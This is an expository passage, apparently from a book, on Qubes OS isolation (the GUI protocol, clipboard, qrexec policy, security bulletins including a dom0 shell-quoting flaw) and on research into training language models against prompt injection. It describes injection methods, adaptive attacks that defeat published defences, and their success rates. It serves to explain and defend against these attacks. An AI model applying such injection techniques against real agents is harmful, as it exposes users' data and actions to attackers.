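Rutkowska and Wojtczuk, of the security company Invisible Things Lab, described the system's design in *Qubes OS Architecture* (2010). On the main desktop systems of the time, an attacker who took over the browser could usually reach the rest of the user's data, and one who took over a wireless driver controlled the machine. Rutkowska and Wojtczuk did not believe anyone could patch all the bugs responsible, so they wanted a system that would limit the damage. Building one from scratch would have taken too long, so they used virtual machines, which let them reuse existing applications and drivers. They also expected virtual machines to be better isolated from each other than ordinary processes are, because a hypervisor does much less than a conventional kernel. It provides no file system or networking, for example, so a hostile program has fewer functions to search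 for bugs.

The designers of Qubes chose the Xen hypervisor over KVM, which turns the Linux kernel into a hypervisor. Xen is far smaller than Linux, so it is easier to review. It also lets drivers run outside dom0. In Qubes, the network card belongs to an unprivileged net qube, and a hardware feature that Intel calls VT-d stops the card from writing to other qubes' memory. An attacker in a hotel who exploits the wireless driver gains control of the net qube and can then cut the connection or read unencrypted traffic, but anyone running the hotel's network could already do both.

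Rutkowska and Wojtczuk relied on manual review and a small hypervisor because they did not expect a mathematical proof of the hypervisor's correctness. The recent proof of the seL4 kernel covered a version for ARM processors, not PCs, and a proof for PCs would need a model of the processor and chipset. They noted that Qubes could switch to a proven hypervisor later and keep the rest of its design.

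The user decides how to divide the work. One suggested setup has separate virtual machines, called qubes, for casual browsing, social accounts, shopping, banking and a job. A related recommendation is to group tasks that expose the same secret. For instance, if two shopping sites have the same credit card number and one steals it, having kept the other in a separate qube helps little.

### From an application to the screen

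When a word processor in a qube called *work* opens a window, it connects to an X server inside the same qube, as it would on any Linux desktop. According to Qubes OS's *GUI virtualization*, this server has no real screen. Its video driver draws into memory, and the server keeps a complete image of each window even if another window covers it.

Each qube has its own pair of programs that connect it to the desktop. One, qubes-gui, runs in the qube and reports each new window. The other, qubes-guid, runs in dom0 and opens a matching window on the real screen. They communicate through memory that Xen lets two virtual machines share.

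Copying pixels into these messages would make video slow, so the qube grants access to the memory pages that hold the picture. qubes-gui sends the grants' reference numbers, and qubes-guid has Xen map the pages into dom0, where the real X server can draw from them. When part of the picture changes, qubes-gui sends the coordinates of the rectangle to repaint.

A compromised qube could send false reference numbers to try to display or corrupt another qube's memory. When qubes-guid asks Xen to map the pages, it therefore includes the identity of the qube that should own them, which it supplies itself rather than taking from the message. Xen maps only pages that qube has granted, so numbers that refer to any other memory are useless. An older version of the protocol used physical memory addresses. It also checked ownership, but it needed a function that only dom0 may use, because the function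 can read any virtual machine's memory.

Since qubes-guid receives data from machines that may be hostile, the designers kept its protocol small. The documentation lists 15 kinds of message from a qube, compared with 120 operations in the basic X protocol. All but three have a fixed size, which simplifies the code that reads them. A window title is limited to 128 bytes of printable characters, and by default these can only be unaccented Latin letters, digits and common symbols. The programmers named the length field in each message `untrusted_len` to remind anyone editing the code that the qube can put any number there.

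Finally, dom0's window manager draws a coloured frame around the window and starts its title with the qube's name in square brackets. The user picks the colour when creating the qube. Menus and similar pop-ups bypass the window manager, so qubes-guid paints a two-pixel frame just inside their edges.

The frame identifies a window's qube but not its program. All the programs in *work* share one X server and can spy on one another, as on any X desktop, so Qubes separates programs only if the user puts them in different qubes.

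A program can also paint a false window, complete with another qube's colours, inside its own. Qubes OS's *Screenshots* argues that this would be very hard in practice because the program doesn't know the exact style of the frames. This defence is weak because many people keep the default style and an attacker can install the same release. The page also suggests better checks, such as dragging a suspicious window onto an empty part of the desktop, since a painted one can't leave the window that contains it, or pressing a key that spreads out all the real windows. The window manager also never lets a qube take over the whole screen, so the outer title bar stays visible, but as with the reserved band in EWS, this works only if the user checks.

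### A keystroke on the way back

When the user types in the *work* window, the keystroke goes first to dom0. The X server there delivers it to the window with keyboard focus, which belongs to the qubes-guid process for *work*. That process sends a key-press message over its link to qubes-gui, which passes it to a virtual keyboard driver. The X server inside the qube then delivers it to the word processor.

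In Qubes OS, dom0 sends keystrokes only to the qube whose window has focus. A program in another qube can query its own X server for the state of the keyboard, but that server has only the keystrokes that dom0 sent to it. The program can also fake input to other programs in the same qube, but the GUI protocol has no message for sending a keystroke to dom0 or to another qube. Qubes therefore guarantees that input arriving from outside a qube came from the user, but it does not guarantee this for input that a program receives from within its own qube.

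A USB keyboard weakens this if the user keeps USB devices in a separate qube, as many do to protect dom0 from malicious memory sticks. The keystrokes then pass through the USB qube before they reach dom0. Anyone who takes over that qube can record what the user types, and may be able to type commands into any window on the desktop.

### Copying text between qubes

Each qube has an ordinary clipboard, and dom0 holds an additional one for transfers. To move an address from a mail program in *personal* to a letter in *work*, the user does the following:

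1. The user selects the address and presses Ctrl+C, which copies it to the clipboard of *personal*. Other qubes can't read that clipboard.
2. With the *personal* window still in focus, the user presses Ctrl+Shift+C. qubes-guid catches the combination, so the mail program never receives it, and asks qubes-gui for the text. dom0 saves the reply in a file without interpreting it.
3. The user clicks on the *work* window and presses Ctrl+Shift+V. qubes-guid catches this combination too and sends the text to the clipboard of *work*.
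4. The user presses Ctrl+V, and the letter program pastes in the normal way.

The original design of the Qubes clipboard kept copied text in a dedicated file instead of dom0's clipboard, so that nobody would paste untrusted text into a dom0 program by mistake. The receiving qube also did the final paste automatically, a step the current version leaves to the user.

The extra key combinations work much like a secure attention key, because no program in a qube can block or imitate them. A background qube cannot read or replace the shared text. But dom0 cannot check what the source qube supplies at the second step. If malware controls *personal*, it can substitute a different address, and the user will find out only by reading the result. After the third step, every program in *work* can read the text, even if the user never pastes it, whereas EWS would have given it to a single program.

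The danger also depends on the direction of the copy. Copying a password from a well-protected qube to a less secure one exposes the password. Copying text the other way may carry an attack into the protected qube, if the text exploits a bug in the program that receives it or contains a shell command. Rutkowska and Wojtczuk left the user to decide what to copy and where. Current versions let an administrator restrict these choices through policy. Tweakers' *Qubes OS 4.2.0* reported that release 4.2.0 added an option to clear the clipboard automatically.

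### qrexec and its policy

Copying a file to another qube, opening a document there and attaching a USB stick all use qrexec, which lets a program in one qube request a service from another. The caller names the service, such as `qubes.Filecopy`, and the target qube runs its own program to handle it, so the caller can't choose an arbitrary command.

The request goes to a trusted program in dom0, which looks for a matching rule in the policy. A few rules might look like this:

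```
qubes.Filecopy   *   mail   vault     deny
qubes.Filecopy   *   mail   @anyvm    ask
qubes.Gpg        *   mail   keys      allow
```

The columns give the service, its argument (here, any), the calling qube, the target and the decision. The first rule that matches applies, and dom0 refuses a request that matches none. Under these rules, *mail* can never send a file to *vault*, and can send one to any other qube only if the user agrees. After dom0 approves a connection, data passes between the two qubes without dom0 having to interpret it.

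The third rule is for Split GPG, which keeps encryption keys in a separate qube, much as EWS gave keys to a separate trusted program. The mail program sends a message to *keys* and gets back a signed copy. Malware in *mail* can't steal the key, but it can get its own messages signed for as long as it controls the qube. An allow rule also exposes the service's code to whatever the caller sends. In September 2021 the project published a bulletin about a fatal flaw in how Split GPG filtered the options it received.

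If the rule is *ask*, dom0 in a default installation draws a dialog that names the calling qube and the requested service and lets the user choose among the targets that the policy permits. A compromised caller can choose the service and any argument, within a restricted set of characters, and can request a particular target. It can also time the request, perhaps for just when the user expects a genuine one. To make accidental approval less likely, the OK button stays inactive for about a second after the dialog gets the focus.

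The caller can't change its own name in the *ask* dialog, because dom0 takes the name from the connection on which the request arrived. SS7 has no such check. A fake *ask* dialog is as harmless as a fake consent prompt in Windows, because only the qube that drew it receives the click.

However, the dialog doesn't show which file the caller will send. If the user asks *mail* to copy an invoice to *work*, malware in *mail* can send an infected file instead, and the prompt will still be accurate and match what the user expects.

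Policy mistakes can be more serious than a hasty click because an allow rule produces no prompt. SecureDrop's *Advisory* of November 2026 describes one in SecureDrop Workstation, a Qubes-based system that journalists use to receive documents from anonymous sources. When a journalist plugged in a memory stick, the USB qube sent a request to attach it to an offline qube called *sd-devices*, which then called back with the port number. The policy also allowed *sd-devices* to make this call without first receiving a request. Malware in *sd-devices* could therefore specify any other port and gain access to a webcam or a Bluetooth adapter, which might give the offline qube a way to send data out.

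SecureDrop did not know of anyone exploiting the flaw, and the attacker would first have had to take over the qube. Qubes enforced the rule as written. The port number was only a name, like the file name that Tymshare's customer gave the compiler, and the authority came from a general rule. If the USB qube had passed *sd-devices* a capability for the one device, *sd-devices* would have had no port number to change.

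### A hostile PDF and a password store

Suppose a user reads email in a qube called *mail* and keeps passwords in *vault*, a qube without a network connection. A stranger sends a PDF that exploits a bug in the PDF viewer. The user right-clicks the attachment and chooses to open it in a disposable qube. Qubes creates the disposable, copies the file into it, opens the file in the viewer there, and destroys the qube afterwards.

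Nothing stops the exploit from working. The attacker now controls the disposable and can read the PDF, which the attacker wrote, but none of the user's other mail. If the malware looks for the passwords, it meets these obstacles:

| Attempt | What stops it | What could get past the protection |
|---|---|---|
| Open the password file | *vault* has a separate virtual disk that the disposable can't reach | A flaw in Xen or the processor |
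| Record the master password as the user types it | dom0 sends those keystrokes only to *vault* | Control of dom0, or of the USB qube if the keyboard is connected through it |
| Copy the picture of the password window | The disposable's X server holds only the disposable's windows | Control of dom0, or a processor flaw that leaks memory |
| Read a password that the user is copying to a browser | dom0 gives the text only to the window where the user presses Ctrl+Shift+V | The user pastes into the disposable by mistake |
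| Call a service in *vault* | A deny rule | A rule that is too broad, or an *ask* rule and a careless click |
| Show a false request for the master password | The frame and title identify the disposable, but Qubes can't stop it from drawing the request | The user doesn't look at them |

An approved file copy could let the attacker put an infected file into *vault* but not fetch the passwords, because `qubes.Filecopy` sends files from the caller to the target. The false prompt is probably the easiest attempt to carry out. It might capture the master password but not the file the password unlocks, so the attacker would still need to get into *vault* or find somewhere else the user has used the same password.

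If the disposable has a network connection, the malware can use it to attack other machines. A February 2019 bulletin concerned an insecure default for this network setting. If the user edits the document, Qubes sends the changed file back to *mail*, and that copy may be as dangerous as the original. Qubes includes a converter that makes a safer copy. A disposable turns each page into plain pixels, and the receiving qube builds a new PDF from them. The new file can't carry the old exploit, but its text becomes an image.

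All this depends on the user right-clicking the attachment. If the user double-clicks it and *mail* is set to open it in its own viewer, the malware gets access to the whole mailbox. The passwords in *vault* are still safe, but the attacker may not need them, because many websites will send a password reset link to that mailbox.

### Costs and limits

The Qubes OS page *Security-critical code* puts the system's trusted computing base at hundreds of thousands of lines of C, compared with tens of millions for Windows, Linux or Mac OS. It calls this several orders of magnitude smaller, though by its own figures the difference is about two. The page leaves dom0's X server and window manager off its list of trusted parts, although they can control every window on the desktop. This is presumably because a qube can reach them only through qubes-guid.

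Much of the trusted code in Qubes OS comes from outside the project. The developers admit that they lack the resources to review Xen thoroughly and more or less trust it blindly. They also trust the distributors of the software inside the qubes, mainly the Fedora Project. Many qubes share one template, a common copy of the operating system, so a back door in the template would reach all of them. But a qube can't permanently change its template, so restarting the qube removes any malware from the system files. Malware in the user's own folder, for instance in a startup script, survives a restart.

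Qubes OS needs enough memory to run several operating systems at once. OpenNET's *Обновление ОС Qubes 4.3.2, использующей виртуализацию для изоляции приложений* (2026), a Russian news report on the October release, gives a minimum of 6 GB and recommends 16 GB. The processor must support virtualization and be able to control devices' access to memory. Intel graphics are the safest choice because the project has tested others less. Applications normally run without the graphics card's 3D acceleration, since sharing the card would add complicated code to dom0.

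The user's judgement also limits the protection Qubes provides. Rutkowska and Wojtczuk describe a colleague sending an infected PDF that the user opens in their work qube. Qubes keeps the infection away from the user's banking and family photographs, but every document in the work qube is exposed. Finer divisions would help, but the user would have more windows to manage, more transfers to make and more chances to choose the wrong qube. Someone who signs in to the bank from the casual browsing qube because it is already open loses the protection, and no policy rule prevents this.

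### Moving the display out of dom0

In 2010, the designers considered moving the display into a separate virtual machine and decided against it. Whoever controls the display can read every window and type into every qube, so they saw little benefit in protecting dom0 from the display. Separation might have kept an intruder from making permanent changes to the system, but they thought that was too small a gain for the added complexity.

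Ten years later, Qubes OS's developers had come to favour a GUI domain, a qube that draws the desktop and has limited powers over the others. They worried that a full desktop in dom0 would tempt users to do risky things, such as setting a downloaded picture as wallpaper, which could expose dom0 to a bug in an image library. Some monitor cables carry data in both directions, so a malicious display could attack the machine. An organisation might also want to give its staff a desktop without giving them control of the whole computer.

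The plan needed two changes elsewhere. The protocol moved from memory addresses to grants, because a GUI domain that could read any memory, as dom0 can, would have been a second dom0. The GUI domain also had to start applications in other qubes without being able to run arbitrary commands in them. The qrexec service `qubes.StartApp` therefore runs only applications that the target qube has listed, and policy can restrict them further.

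The graphics card has been harder. Ideally the GUI domain would control it directly, but most cards failed when the developers tried this, often because their startup code requires full access to the machine. A second design sends the desktop over a network to another computer. It worked, but it doesn't help someone sitting at the machine, because dom0 runs the local screen and has no network. The third design is a compromise in which dom0 keeps the graphics driver and an X server but runs only one full-screen program, which displays the GUI domain's desktop. This removes large desktop libraries from dom0.

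Release 4.1 included the compromise as an experimental feature, switched off by default. The current release is 4.3.2, from October 2026. According to the documentation for the 4.3 series, dom0's window manager still draws the frames, and the GUI description says qubes-guid runs in dom0 by default. Most users therefore still have the 2010 arrangement. A GUI domain would make a successful attack on the desktop easier to contain and clean up, but the attacker would still see everything the user sees, so the 2010 objection still partly applies.

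### What the security bulletins record

The list of Qubes OS security bulletins goes back to May 2011, and most of the recent ones concern code and hardware that the project did not make. All three bulletins from 2025 were about processors. Of the nine from March to August 2026, four concerned processors and three concerned Xen. The list is an incomplete record of faults because the project does not treat attacks that only crash the system as security issues.

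The July 2025 bulletin covered a family of processor flaws found by researchers at Microsoft and ETH Zurich. According to Linux Compatible's *QSB-108*, an attacker who controlled one qube could measure how long certain instructions took and deduce the contents of any memory in the system. Rutkowska and Wojtczuk had anticipated the general problem. They worried less about covert channels, in which two hostile programs signal to each other, than about a hostile program spying on an innocent one through the processor's cache. Keeping qubes on separate processors would help, but it would slow the system, and in practice users depend on fixes from Intel, AMD and Xen.

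Xen has also failed at its main function, keeping qubes' memory separate. Intruder's *CVE-2026-119783*, an automatically generated summary, describes a flaw from November 2026 in which Xen could free a page of memory and give it to a new owner before fully removing the old owner's access. A compromised qube might then read or change data in a page it no longer owned. A check on who owns a page, like the one in the display protocol, can't protect against this because Xen itself enforces the check.

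Bugs in the project's own interface are rarer but affect the trusted path more directly. Two bulletins in September and October 2021 concerned the flag that marks a window as a menu. The window manager in dom0 frames ordinary windows and qubes-guid frames menus, so a window can have no frame if the two programs disagree about which kind it is. In October 2024 another bulletin reported missing frames under KDE, an alternative desktop, on windows from the small helper machines that emulate hardware for some qubes. Earlier clipboard problems included a leak between qubes in 2014 and timing attacks described in a January 2015 bulletin.

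Linux Compatible's *QSB-111* (2026) describes a flaw in the Qubes OS screen lock, reported in April 2026. Someone with physical access and an automated device could, in theory, send commands fast enough to disable the lock before it fully took effect. The attack does not require a flaw in Xen or a hostile qube, and it would give the intruder the same access to the desktop as the user.

*Qubes Security Bulletin 118* (August 2026) describes a mistake in how dom0 handles file-copy errors. When a user copies a file from dom0 to a qube with `qvm-copy-to-vm`, the receiving qube replies with a checksum, an error code and the name of the last file it received. If there was an error, dom0 shows a dialog that includes this name. A compromised qube could report an error and invent the name, which dom0 would then display.

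The program in dom0 first replaced double quotation marks, control characters and non-ASCII characters in the name with underscores. It then put the name between single quotation marks in a shell command that opened the dialog. A single quotation mark in the name could end the quoted text early, and the shell would run what followed as a command in dom0. SQL injection exploits the same kind of mistake. The attack worked only if the user copied something from dom0 to the compromised qube, which most people seldom do. But the flaw affected every release, and because dom0 is the most privileged part of Qubes, a successful attack gave the attacker control of the whole machine.

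The version of the tool that runs inside ordinary qubes did not have the flaw. It starts the dialog program directly and passes the message as a separate argument, so no shell interprets the file name.

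## Training language models to separate instructions from data

Unlike the safe version of the Qubes copy tool, a language model has no separate place for data, so it can distinguish instructions from data in its context window only as well as its training allows. Researchers have been working on this training since 2024. The best-trained models now resist most injected instructions, even when an attacker has hundreds of attempts, but no training method gives the guarantee that a parameterised query does.

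### Role marks

An application sends a model a list of messages, each with a role. The system role is for the developer's instructions, the user role for the person's requests and the tool role for whatever a tool has fetched. *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* (Pirch, Horlboge and colleagues, 2026) describes how this list grows in agents similar to OpenClaw, a popular open-source assistant. The ordinary software around the model starts the list with a system prompt and the user's message, then sends it to the model. If the model replies with a tool call, the software runs the tool, adds the result to the list and sends the whole list back to the model. This continues until the task is finished or the agent reaches a step limit.

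Before the model processes the list of messages, a library turns it into one string. Special tokens mark where each message begins and which role it has. A search result, for example, becomes a token that marks a tool message, then the text of the page, then a token that marks the end.

Software can make these marks hard to forge. Chen, Peng and colleagues (2026) note in *SecPO* that a well-written library stops any message from breaking out of its role. If an email contains the characters of a system mark, the library can encode them as ordinary text. This resembles a parameterised query, except that a database also guarantees that a value can't act as a command, while nothing in a language model guarantees this for the text of a tool message. The mark is one more token in the sequence, and its effect depends on the model's weights, the numbers that training adjusts. It only makes the model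 less likely to obey commands in a tool message, whereas dom0 does not carry out a request that a Qubes policy denies.

Written warnings have the same weakness. The instructions for agents like OpenClaw usually include security rules, but Pirch and colleagues point out that only the model enforces them, so later text can override them. All four agents they tested put trusted and untrusted text into one context.

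The software also has to give each message the right role. Models learn to give privileged text more influence, so correct labelling is a security requirement, as *When Context Gets Root* (2026) points out. The software that Pirch and colleagues describe builds the system prompt partly from stored memory and session history, so an agent's own notes and summaries can come back as instructions.

### The instruction hierarchy

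Early chat models often gave a developer's instructions no more weight than text from a web page. In *The Instruction Hierarchy*, Wallace, Xiao and colleagues at OpenAI (2024) tried to change this by ranking system messages highest, followed by user messages, the model's own outputs and finally tool outputs. When two instructions conflict, the model should follow the higher-ranked one.

The model has to judge whether a lower-ranking instruction is compatible with those above it, because if it ignored all such instructions, users could not ask it for anything. If a developer has set up a car sales assistant, it should comply when a customer asks it to speak Spanish, but ignore the instruction or refuse when the customer tells it to sell a car for $1.

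Wallace and colleagues generated training examples for compatible and conflicting instructions. For compatible instructions, they took a request, such as one for a 20-line poem in Spanish, split it into parts and placed the parts at different ranks. They trained the model to give the answer it would have given to the whole request. For conflicting instructions, they trained it to answer as if it had never seen the lower-ranking one. They treated every instruction in a web page as conflicting. They used a second model to insert instructions into search results and trained the first to give its original answer.

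They applied this to GPT-3.5 Turbo. The model's defence against attempts to extract the system prompt improved by 63%. Its resistance to jailbreaks, in which users try to get a model to break its safety rules, improved by over 30%, although the training examples included no jailbreaks. The model also began to refuse some harmless requests.

Wallace and colleagues compared language models without an instruction hierarchy to a computer on which every program runs in kernel mode, with full control of the machine. Their hierarchy protects less reliably than the separation in operating systems, because a processor enforces kernel mode regardless of what a program contains, while the model applies the hierarchy by interpreting the untrusted text itself. Later work has added ranks. *Training LLMs to Enforce Multi-Level Instruction Hierarchies via Gravity-Weighted Direct Preference Optimization*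 (2026) uses five and treats violations near the top as more severe, but it still relies on what the model learns.

### Reserved delimiters and preference training

Sizhe Chen and David Wagner, of the University of California, Berkeley, have worked with various colleagues on a stricter rule, under which the model follows no instructions in the data. Their first system, StruQ, appeared at a security conference in 2025. *Intent-Aware Protection for AI Agents* (Copty, Haiby and colleagues, 2026) describes its two parts. A front end puts instructions and data into separate structured channels, and fine-tuning (further training) teaches the model to follow instructions only from the prompt channel.

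The front end reserves certain tokens as delimiters and removes them from the data, so an attacker cannot use them to end the data part early. In SQL injection, a quotation mark in the data ends a string early in the same way. The model could still follow an instruction within the data, so it is fine-tuned on examples in which the data contains an instruction and the correct answer ignores it.

Fine-tuning of this kind shows the model only correct answers. SecAlign, the group's next system, also shows it the wrong answer, so that training can make one more likely and the other less. Chen and colleagues describe how a later version, Meta-SecAlign, prepares its examples:

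1. Take a request and some data, such as a request to summarise a restaurant review.
2. Insert an instruction from an unrelated example at the beginning or end of the review.
3. Give the original model the clean review, and keep its summary as the good answer.
4. Give the original model the unrelated task by itself, and keep the result as the bad answer.

No person has to write or grade the answers. Training then minimises a quantity known as the direct preference optimisation (DPO) loss:

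```
loss = -log σ( β × [ log p(good | injected) - log p0(good | injected) ]
             - β × [ log p(bad  | injected) - log p0(bad  | injected) ] )
```

Here p is the probability that the model in training gives an answer, and p0 is the probability that the original model gives it. "Injected" means that both models see the review with the inserted instruction. The function σ maps any number to one between 0 and 1, and β sets how strongly the comparison with the original model counts. The loss falls as the model in training becomes more likely than the original to give the good answer and less likely to give the bad one. Using the original model as a reference also discourages large changes that might damage the model's other abilities.

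### Different embeddings for data

ASIDE, which Egor Zverev and colleagues proposed in 2025, changes the first step of a model's processing, whereas StruQ and SecAlign leave the model's internal design unchanged. A model begins by converting each token into a list of numbers called an embedding. Normally the word "delete" gets the same embedding whether the developer or a stranger wrote it, and the model has to infer the source from the surrounding marks. ASIDE rotates the embeddings of data tokens, so every token has one embedding as an instruction and another as data. The surrounding software chooses between them according to where the text came from, so a stranger who writes the text can't control which one is used.

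ASIDE's rotation directly indicates the source of every token, which a mark at the start of a message does not. Pant, Lohani and Kumar (2026), in *On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models*, credit ASIDE with the unforgeable separation that their theory requires. That seems too generous, because the rotation happens at the model's input and later layers still combine information from instructions and data. ASIDE identifies which tokens are data, but the model must still learn from examples not to obey them.

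### Attackers who adapt

Developers usually tested these defences against a fixed set of known attacks. *The Attacker Moves Second* (2025), by Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, including researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind, showed that such tests reveal little about how a defence performs against an attacker who adapts to it. The paper tested 12 published defences against jailbreaks and prompt injection, including StruQ and Meta-SecAlign. Most had originally reported attack success rates near zero, but adaptive attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the 12.

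Two of the 12 defenses relied only on how the developer worded or arranged the prompt. Fixed attacks succeeded against these as rarely as 1% of the time, and adaptive attacks succeeded over 95% of the time. The group also held an online competition with more than 500 participants. Participants found successful attacks in every scenario, while the fixed attacks succeeded in none.

A fixed test uses attacks that worked on some earlier model. A model can pass by learning to recognise those attacks or similar ones, without learning to separate instructions from data. The guard circuit on AT&T's trunks was similarly limited because it dealt only with accidental tones. A real attacker can see that an attempt has failed and try something else, so a defence should be measured against the best attack anyone can find.

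The results also have limits. Nasr and colleagues gave attackers large computing budgets because they wanted to know whether each defence could fail, not how much effort that would take. They also warn that the figures can't be compared across defences, since they tested each one roughly as its developers had. But they checked the successful attacks by hand, and a defence that fails after a day's computing would not protect anything valuable.

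### SecPO

SecPO is the Berkeley group's response, published in October 2026. It changes both what Meta-SecAlign trains towards and what it trains on.

Chen and colleagues trace part of Meta-SecAlign's weakness to its reference model. The DPO loss compares the model in training with the original model on injected text, which is where the original model behaves badly. The comparison therefore holds the new model close to behaviour that it is supposed to lose. An ideal model would treat injected text exactly as the original treats the same text with the injection removed. Nobody has such a model, but the developers insert the injections themselves, so they still have the clean text and can calculate how the ideal model would respond. SecPO puts those values into the loss:

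```
loss = -log σ( β × [ log p(good | injected) - log p0(good | clean) ]
             - β × [ log p(bad  | injected) - log p0(bad  | clean) ] )
```

Suppose the original model is nine times as likely to give the bad answer as the good one when the review contains an injection, and only a thousandth as likely when it does not. DPO measures progress from the first ratio, so even a modest improvement counts. SecPO measures progress from the second. For any one example, both losses move the weights in the same direction, but SecPO moves them more on the examples where the injection had most affected the original model.

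SecPO also trains on stronger attacks. For each example, an attacking model generates eight injections, a judging model scores how well each one works, and the attacking model generates eight more. After 30 rounds, or 240 attempts, the model in training learns from the most successful injection. This process took 18 hours on 16 high-end graphics processors for Llama-3.1-8B-Instruct, a small open model. Chen and colleagues then reused the examples to train a larger model, Qwen3.6-27B, in 7 hours on eight processors.

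The table gives their main results for the larger model. The first five rows show how often attacks succeeded, and the last three show performance on ordinary work with no attack.

| Test | Undefended | Meta-SecAlign | SecPO |
|---|---|---|---|
| SEP, instructions hidden in text: fixed attacks | 98.9% | 2.9% | 1.8% |
| SEP: adaptive attack, up to 800 attempts | 100.0% | 93.7% | 13.3% |
| AgentDojo, agents using tools: fixed attacks | 26.9% | 2.2% | 0.0% |
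| AgentDojo: adaptive attack, up to 800 attempts | 81.3% | 78.8% | 8.8% |
| DTaP-Bench, harder agent tasks: fixed attacks | 50.8% | 45.9% | 7.6% |
| AgentDojo: tasks completed | 89.7% | 87.6% | 90.7% |
| AgentDyn, tasks that require replanning: tasks completed | 71.7% | 76.7% | 71.7% |
| Average of six tests of science, mathematics and following instructions | 88.9% | 88.4% | 89.1% |

Meta-SecAlign performed almost as well as SecPO against the fixed attacks in SEP and AgentDojo, but hardly better than no defence against the adaptive ones. SecPO reduced usefulness very little. The largest drop on the ordinary tests was 0.9 percentage points, on school mathematics problems. The stronger training examples and the new loss both contributed to the security. With the stronger examples but the old loss, the adaptive attack on SEP succeeded 60.9% of the time, compared with 13.3% for the full method.

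The developers made these measurements themselves, but they took more care than most. They excluded the attack methods used in training from the adaptive tests and rebuilt the method from *The Attacker Moves Second*, whose author confirmed the reproduction. On SEP, they counted an attack as successful only if nine separate judgements by other models all agreed that it was. Such a strict rule could miss successful attacks, but the developers checked 1,024 outputs by hand and found none that it had missed.

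The 8.8% success rate in the adaptive AgentDojo test represents seven successful attacks in 80 cases, so the true rate could plausibly be anywhere from about 4% to 17%. Successful attacks cost an average of $5.92 against the undefended model and $34.90 against SecPO. The higher cost might discourage someone who sends injections to thousands of strangers, but not someone who wants one executive's mailbox. Outside researchers have also had little time to attack SecPO, and several of the defences that Nasr and colleagues defeated had once looked strong too.

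The group tested the model with its step-by-step reasoning switched off, although many agents depend on reasoning. They also assumed that the software always labels untrusted text correctly. They do not consider prompt injection solved, and observe that some commercial models gain security by refusing too often. Anthropic's Opus 5.0 completed 70.0% of the AgentDyn tasks, slightly fewer than the much smaller undefended Qwen model, while OpenAI's GPT-5.5 completed 83.3%.

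### Whether separation is impossible

Data can change a system's output without giving it commands. A database returns different results when its records change, but it doesn't run those records as queries. Some researchers still argue that no amount of training can separate instructions from data in a language model. Schneier wrote in 2024 that this separation, which worked for the telephone network, can't work for a language model because the model is useful precisely for letting data change what it does. His argument implies that a model must let an email affect its summary of that email, but not that the email must be able to make the model send one. He ended the essay by predicting that a researcher would someday work out how to separate the two paths, so he was describing a limit of current designs rather than a permanent one.

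Pant, Lohani and Kumar offer a proof. They consider a model's control decisions, such as whether to refuse a request, call a tool or write to memory. These decisions may depend on what untrusted text means, but they should not depend on how someone encodes it. If u and v are two pieces of untrusted text with the same meaning, and s is the developer's instructions, then the model should satisfy:

```
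control(s followed by u) = control(s followed by v)
```

The proof covers models that meet three conditions. Instructions and data must pass through the same internal representation. Nothing in the design may enforce a permanent distinction between them. And the control decisions must come from that shared processing. The argument then has three steps:

1. The model can't always tell where text came from. If it has to guess whether a representation is trusted or untrusted, and the two are equally common, the lowest possible error rate is ½ × (1 − TV). TV, the total variation distance, is 0 when trusted and untrusted text produce identical distributions of representations and 1 when the distributions don't overlap at all. The word "the" has one embedding whoever writes it, so at the entrance they do overlap.
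2. Untrusted text affects control decisions. At each layer, the model updates its representation of a token with a weighted sum over the tokens it has read, and that sum includes the untrusted ones.
3. Training covers a finite number of encodings, while the same meaning has an unlimited number. Correct behaviour on the encodings in training therefore does not guarantee correct behaviour on the rest.

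Pant and colleagues conclude that training alone can't guarantee the property for a model of this kind, which follows from the third step of their proof. In the last lines of the proof, they also conclude that the property fails, which does not follow. A model might behave correctly on an encoding that nobody tested. A model that refused every request and never called a tool would also satisfy the property, so the three conditions can't rule out every model that satisfies it.

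Pant and colleagues also leave the first step partly unproven. A single embedding of "the" does not reveal its source, but a model reads the word in context, after a role mark, and they assume that representations in context overlap too. They treat role marks as forgeable, which is true if the surrounding software lets strangers write them, but a front end like StruQ's is designed to prevent that.

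The property also differs from immunity to prompt injection. An assistant that forwarded the user's mail whenever a stranger asked, in any encoding, would satisfy the property because it would behave consistently.

Pant and colleagues do not claim that defences are useless. The proof does not establish how often they fail, and it is compatible with a model that follows one injection in a billion. In a small experiment, Pant and colleagues tried five kinds of injection on two models, and both models refused every time. The injected text changed only such things as the length and tone of the replies.

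Whether a rate like that would be good enough depends on how hard the failing texts are to find. Ordinary email would almost never contain one by chance, but an attacker searches for them. SecPO's results are more informative here than the proof because they measure how often such a search succeeds, which was in roughly one case in ten within 800 attempts. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper by researchers at Google, Nvidia and several universities, conjectures that persistent attackers will always find a way past defences inside the model. It recommends treating the model as untrusted and enforcing security in the software around it. The record since 2024 supports the conjecture as a working assumption, though nobody has proved it.

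The proof does not apply to designs that process trusted and untrusted text separately, or that leave decisions about tools to a program outside the model. One attempt at such a design is to split an agent between two models, only one of which reads untrusted text.

### What counts as separation

Researchers also lack an agreed definition of separation between instructions and data. In 2025, Zverev and colleagues, who designed the SEP test, proposed a measure that compares a model's output when an instruction is in the prompt with its output when the same instruction is in the data. A larger difference means better separation. None of the models they tested scored well. Because the measure is an average, a model could score highly and still fail on a text that an attacker finds. A model could also score highly by refusing to answer whenever the data contained an instruction, so the test has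 to measure usefulness as well.

Chen and colleagues distinguish several goals that defences have pursued. One is for the model to ignore injected instructions entirely, as SecPO trains it to do. This does not work for translation, because a model translating a letter into French must translate the sentence "Send the money today" along with the rest. In such cases, the model should process the instruction as text without obeying it.

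Other tasks require the agent to follow instructions in untrusted data. For example, a user might ask an agent to install a program by following the guide on its website, which consists almost entirely of instructions. The agent has to carry out the instructions that the user's request covers and reject any others, much as a model trained on the instruction hierarchy has to treat a user's request. Chen and colleagues call this an open problem and warn that an instruction can be relevant to a task without being authorised by the user. They examined 140 successful attacks against SecPO in DTaP-Bench, and in 75 of them the agent also completed the user's task, so checking only whether the task was done would not have revealed the attack.

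A model that never followed instructions in its data would still act on the information there. In one AgentDyn task, the user asks an agent to check the rating of some running shoes bought that day and to buy a different pair if the rating is below 4.0. The agent finds a rating of 3.2 and correctly buys another pair for $80.49. But whoever controls the rating also controls whether the agent spends the money. Ignoring instructions in the data doesn't protect against a false rating, because the rating contains no instruction and the user asked the agent to rely on it.

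## Agents that plan without reading untrusted text

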